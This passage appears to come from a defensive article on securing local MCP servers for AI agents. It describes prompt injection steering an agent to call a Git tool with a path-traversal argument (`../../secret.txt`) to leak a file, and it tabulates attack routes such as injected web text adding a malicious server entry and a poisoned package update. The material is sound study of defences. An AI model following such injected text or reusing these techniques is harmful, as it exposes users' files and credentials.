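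Codex may have a similar gap. An older change to its documentation, *Update README.md (#2564)*, warns that Codex runs shell commands in a sandbox by default but runs trusted MCP tool calls outside it. Later versions may behave differently.

VS Code users lose the per-server sandbox if they move an entry to the portable `.mcp.json` format that Copilot reads, because that format doesn't support the setting. Administrators can require Copilot's sandbox on company machines.

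### What an approved server can still disclose

*My Credentials, Please* (October 2026) shows why an honest server needs a sandbox too. In it, Huang, Tang and colleagues looked for local stdio servers that could reveal files unrelated to their purpose. They assumed that the user had started a legitimate server and that an attacker could influence only the arguments of a tool call, for example through prompt injection.

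The researchers found one such flaw, CVE-2026-27735, in Anthropic's Git server. Its `git_add` tool prepares files for the next commit, and its `git_diff_staged` tool displays the prepared changes. An attacker could get the agent to call `git_add` with a path outside the repository, such as `../../secret.txt`. The server would read the file, and `git_diff_staged` would return its contents. Both calls would have looked like ordinary Git operations to a user who approved them.

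The researchers define the flaw by comparing two sets of file accesses. Reach(*t*) contains every access that an attacker can cause through the arguments of tool *t*, and *B*(*t*) contains the accesses that the tool's purpose and setup justify. The tool has the flaw if Reach(*t*) contains any access that is not in *B*(*t*). For `git_add`, reading `../../secret.txt` is one such access.

To test a tool, the researchers put a fake credential outside the folder it needed and ran three cases:

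1. A malicious call without a sandbox had to return the credential.
2. A normal call inside a sandbox had to work.
3. The malicious call inside the same sandbox had to fail to return the credential.

The study started with 21,097 listings from nine registries and classified 4,806 servers that could be run. Of these, 787 (16.4%) could work with files although their main purpose was something else. This is a rough screening figure, because some of these servers may have good reason to save files, such as remembering conversations. A language model then examined the source code of 4,292 servers and flagged 2,818 for possible flaws.

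Testing confirmed 150 cases. In 136, the reply contained the exact text of the fake credential. Other evidence, such as a changed file, confirmed the remaining 14. An ordinary file path was enough in 144 cases, while the other six needed the path inside a valid document, such as a Word file. In 38 cases, the attack bypassed a check already in the server's code.

The study is strong evidence that approved servers can leak files, but it doesn't show how common the problem is. The researchers selected which candidates to test, and the 150 cases count individual tools, several of which could belong to the same server.

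Huang, Tang and colleagues show that a sandbox can stop such leaks in many different servers, but their figures can't support their conclusion that sandboxes "reliably" enforce these limits without disrupting normal use. They counted a case as confirmed only if the sandbox stopped the attack and the normal call still worked, so the 150 confirmed cases would exclude any in which the sandbox failed. They also tested only one sandbox, on macOS, and did not measure the accuracy of the file limits, which a language model drafted.

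Anthropic fixed the `git_add` flaw in version 2026.1.14. The researchers reported 13 findings in total, and many were still awaiting fixes or CVE numbers when they finished the paper.

Under one proposal, each server would declare which files its tools need, so that the client can show this to the user and enforce it. But the declaration would be part of the server's tool list, which the client receives only after starting the server. To restrict the server as soon as it starts, the client needs the information earlier, for example from a catalogue entry.

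### Monitoring which process started which

Monitoring can reveal launches that bypassed the other controls. The operating system records a parent for every process, so a monitor can reconstruct the chain. On a Langflow server, a normal launch and an attack might look like this:

```
langflow -> uvx -> python (mcp-server-fetch)
langflow -> touch
```

If Langflow is supposed to start servers only through the company's launcher, the monitor can raise an alert whenever Langflow starts any other program. This works well on a web server, where the normal pattern of launches rarely changes. On a developer's laptop, a coding assistant starts shells and test programs all day, so the same rule would produce many false alarms.

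The main limit is that the damage is usually done by the time someone reads the alert. `touch` finishes within milliseconds, and a program that steals an SSH key may need only a second or so. The company can still replace the stolen key and find the entry that started the program. A monitor that holds each new process until it decides whether to allow it can prevent the damage, but it needs the same information as the launch check.

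Monitoring also misses attacks that start no unusual process, such as the malicious update to `postmark-mcp`.

Model Context Protocol's security guidance recommends that proxies log all stdio use. Claude Code can export the names of the MCP servers and tools that people use, but users name their own servers, so a record that `github` ran doesn't prove which program it was. A useful record includes the full command, the package's hash, the parent process and the user. The monitor should save the parent when the process starts, because Linux assigns a new parent if the original one exits.

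### The roadmap for local servers

The MCP project plans to change how clients communicate with local servers. Its roadmap, updated on 16 November 2026, proposes "HTTP over stdio" (Model Context Protocol, 2026). The client and server would exchange HTTP messages through the server's input and output streams, so developers would no longer have to maintain separate designs for local and remote servers. The proposal would probably use HTTP/2, which can carry several exchanges over one connection at once.

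This doesn't change who chooses the command. The roadmap explicitly keeps the server as a subprocess, so an entry whose command is `touch` would still create its file before the connection failed.

Nothing on the roadmap restricts which programs a client may start. The next version of the specification is due on 30 March 2027, later than the original target of December 2026. The project describes its plans as subject to change.

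Work on launch security may also come from the Model Context Protocol's Security Interest Group, whose topics include how clients can verify the programs they start, what should happen when a server changes after approval, and how to isolate stdio processes. The group discusses these problems and passes proposals to the teams responsible, so its list of topics is not a commitment to build anything.

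### A worked deployment

Suppose Maria's company runs an agent framework on a web server and gives its developers Claude Code. It combines the controls as follows:

1. Two administrators maintain the catalogue. Neither developers nor agents can change it.
2. The agent framework requires a login and accepts only a catalogue identifier, which it passes to the launcher.
3. Each developer's `managed-mcp.json` contains only entries that call the launcher, such as `/opt/company/launch` with the argument `notes`.
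4. The launcher checks the package's hash and starts the server in a sandbox. The server receives placeholders instead of real credentials.
5. Claude Code runs in a container that holds the current project but no SSH keys or cloud credentials.
6. A monitor records every process that the framework and Claude Code start.

The company has to test the fourth and fifth measures together, because the sandbox tool that Claude Code uses on Linux can fail to start inside a container.

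The table shows what should happen if someone attacks this deployment by each of the six routes. The outcomes are judgements based on how the published attacks worked.

| Route | Attack | Expected result |
|---|---|---|
| Web form | A visitor submits `touch` as a command | The framework refuses the request |
| Injected text | A web page persuades Claude Code to add a `touch` entry to `.mcp.json` | Claude Code may write the entry but doesn't start it |
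| Repository file | A pull request adds a server that runs `touch` | Claude Code ignores the server |
| Package | A publisher releases a malicious update | The launcher keeps using the reviewed version |
| Sign-in address | An approved remote server sends an address that contains a command | If the client has the flaw, the command runs inside the container |
| Web page to local service | A page tells an old copy of MCP Inspector to run `touch` | The command runs, because the Inspector doesn't use the launcher |

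An attack through injected text doesn't need a new server. The text could lead Claude Code to run `touch` in its own terminal, where the container limits the damage but doesn't prevent the command. It could also lead the agent to misuse an approved server, for example by giving an unpatched `git_add` a path outside the project, though the server's sandbox should block that read.

A repository can also run code without an MCP entry. In Datadog's attack, a settings file made Claude Code run the project's own version of `git`. The launcher would not detect this, and the program could read everything in the container, including the source code and any key Claude Code uses to access the model. The company should therefore give the container a key with a spending limit and restrict which hosts it can contact.

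The sign-in attack works only if the attacker controls a remote server that the administrators have approved, because `managed-mcp.json` blocks all other servers. Keeping the client up to date remains the best defence.

To protect developers from the Inspector attack, the company has to find old copies of the Inspector and either remove them or allow the tool to run only inside a container. The monitor in the deployment above would miss the attack because it watches only the framework and Claude Code. If it watched all processes on the laptop, it would probably record the Inspector starting `touch`.

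The package attack succeeds if an administrator approves the malicious update. With `postmark-mcp`, the new hash would match the catalogue, the sandbox would permit the connection to Postmark, and the proxy would supply the real credential. To stop the attack, the reviewer has to notice the added line, or the company has to limit who can receive its emails.
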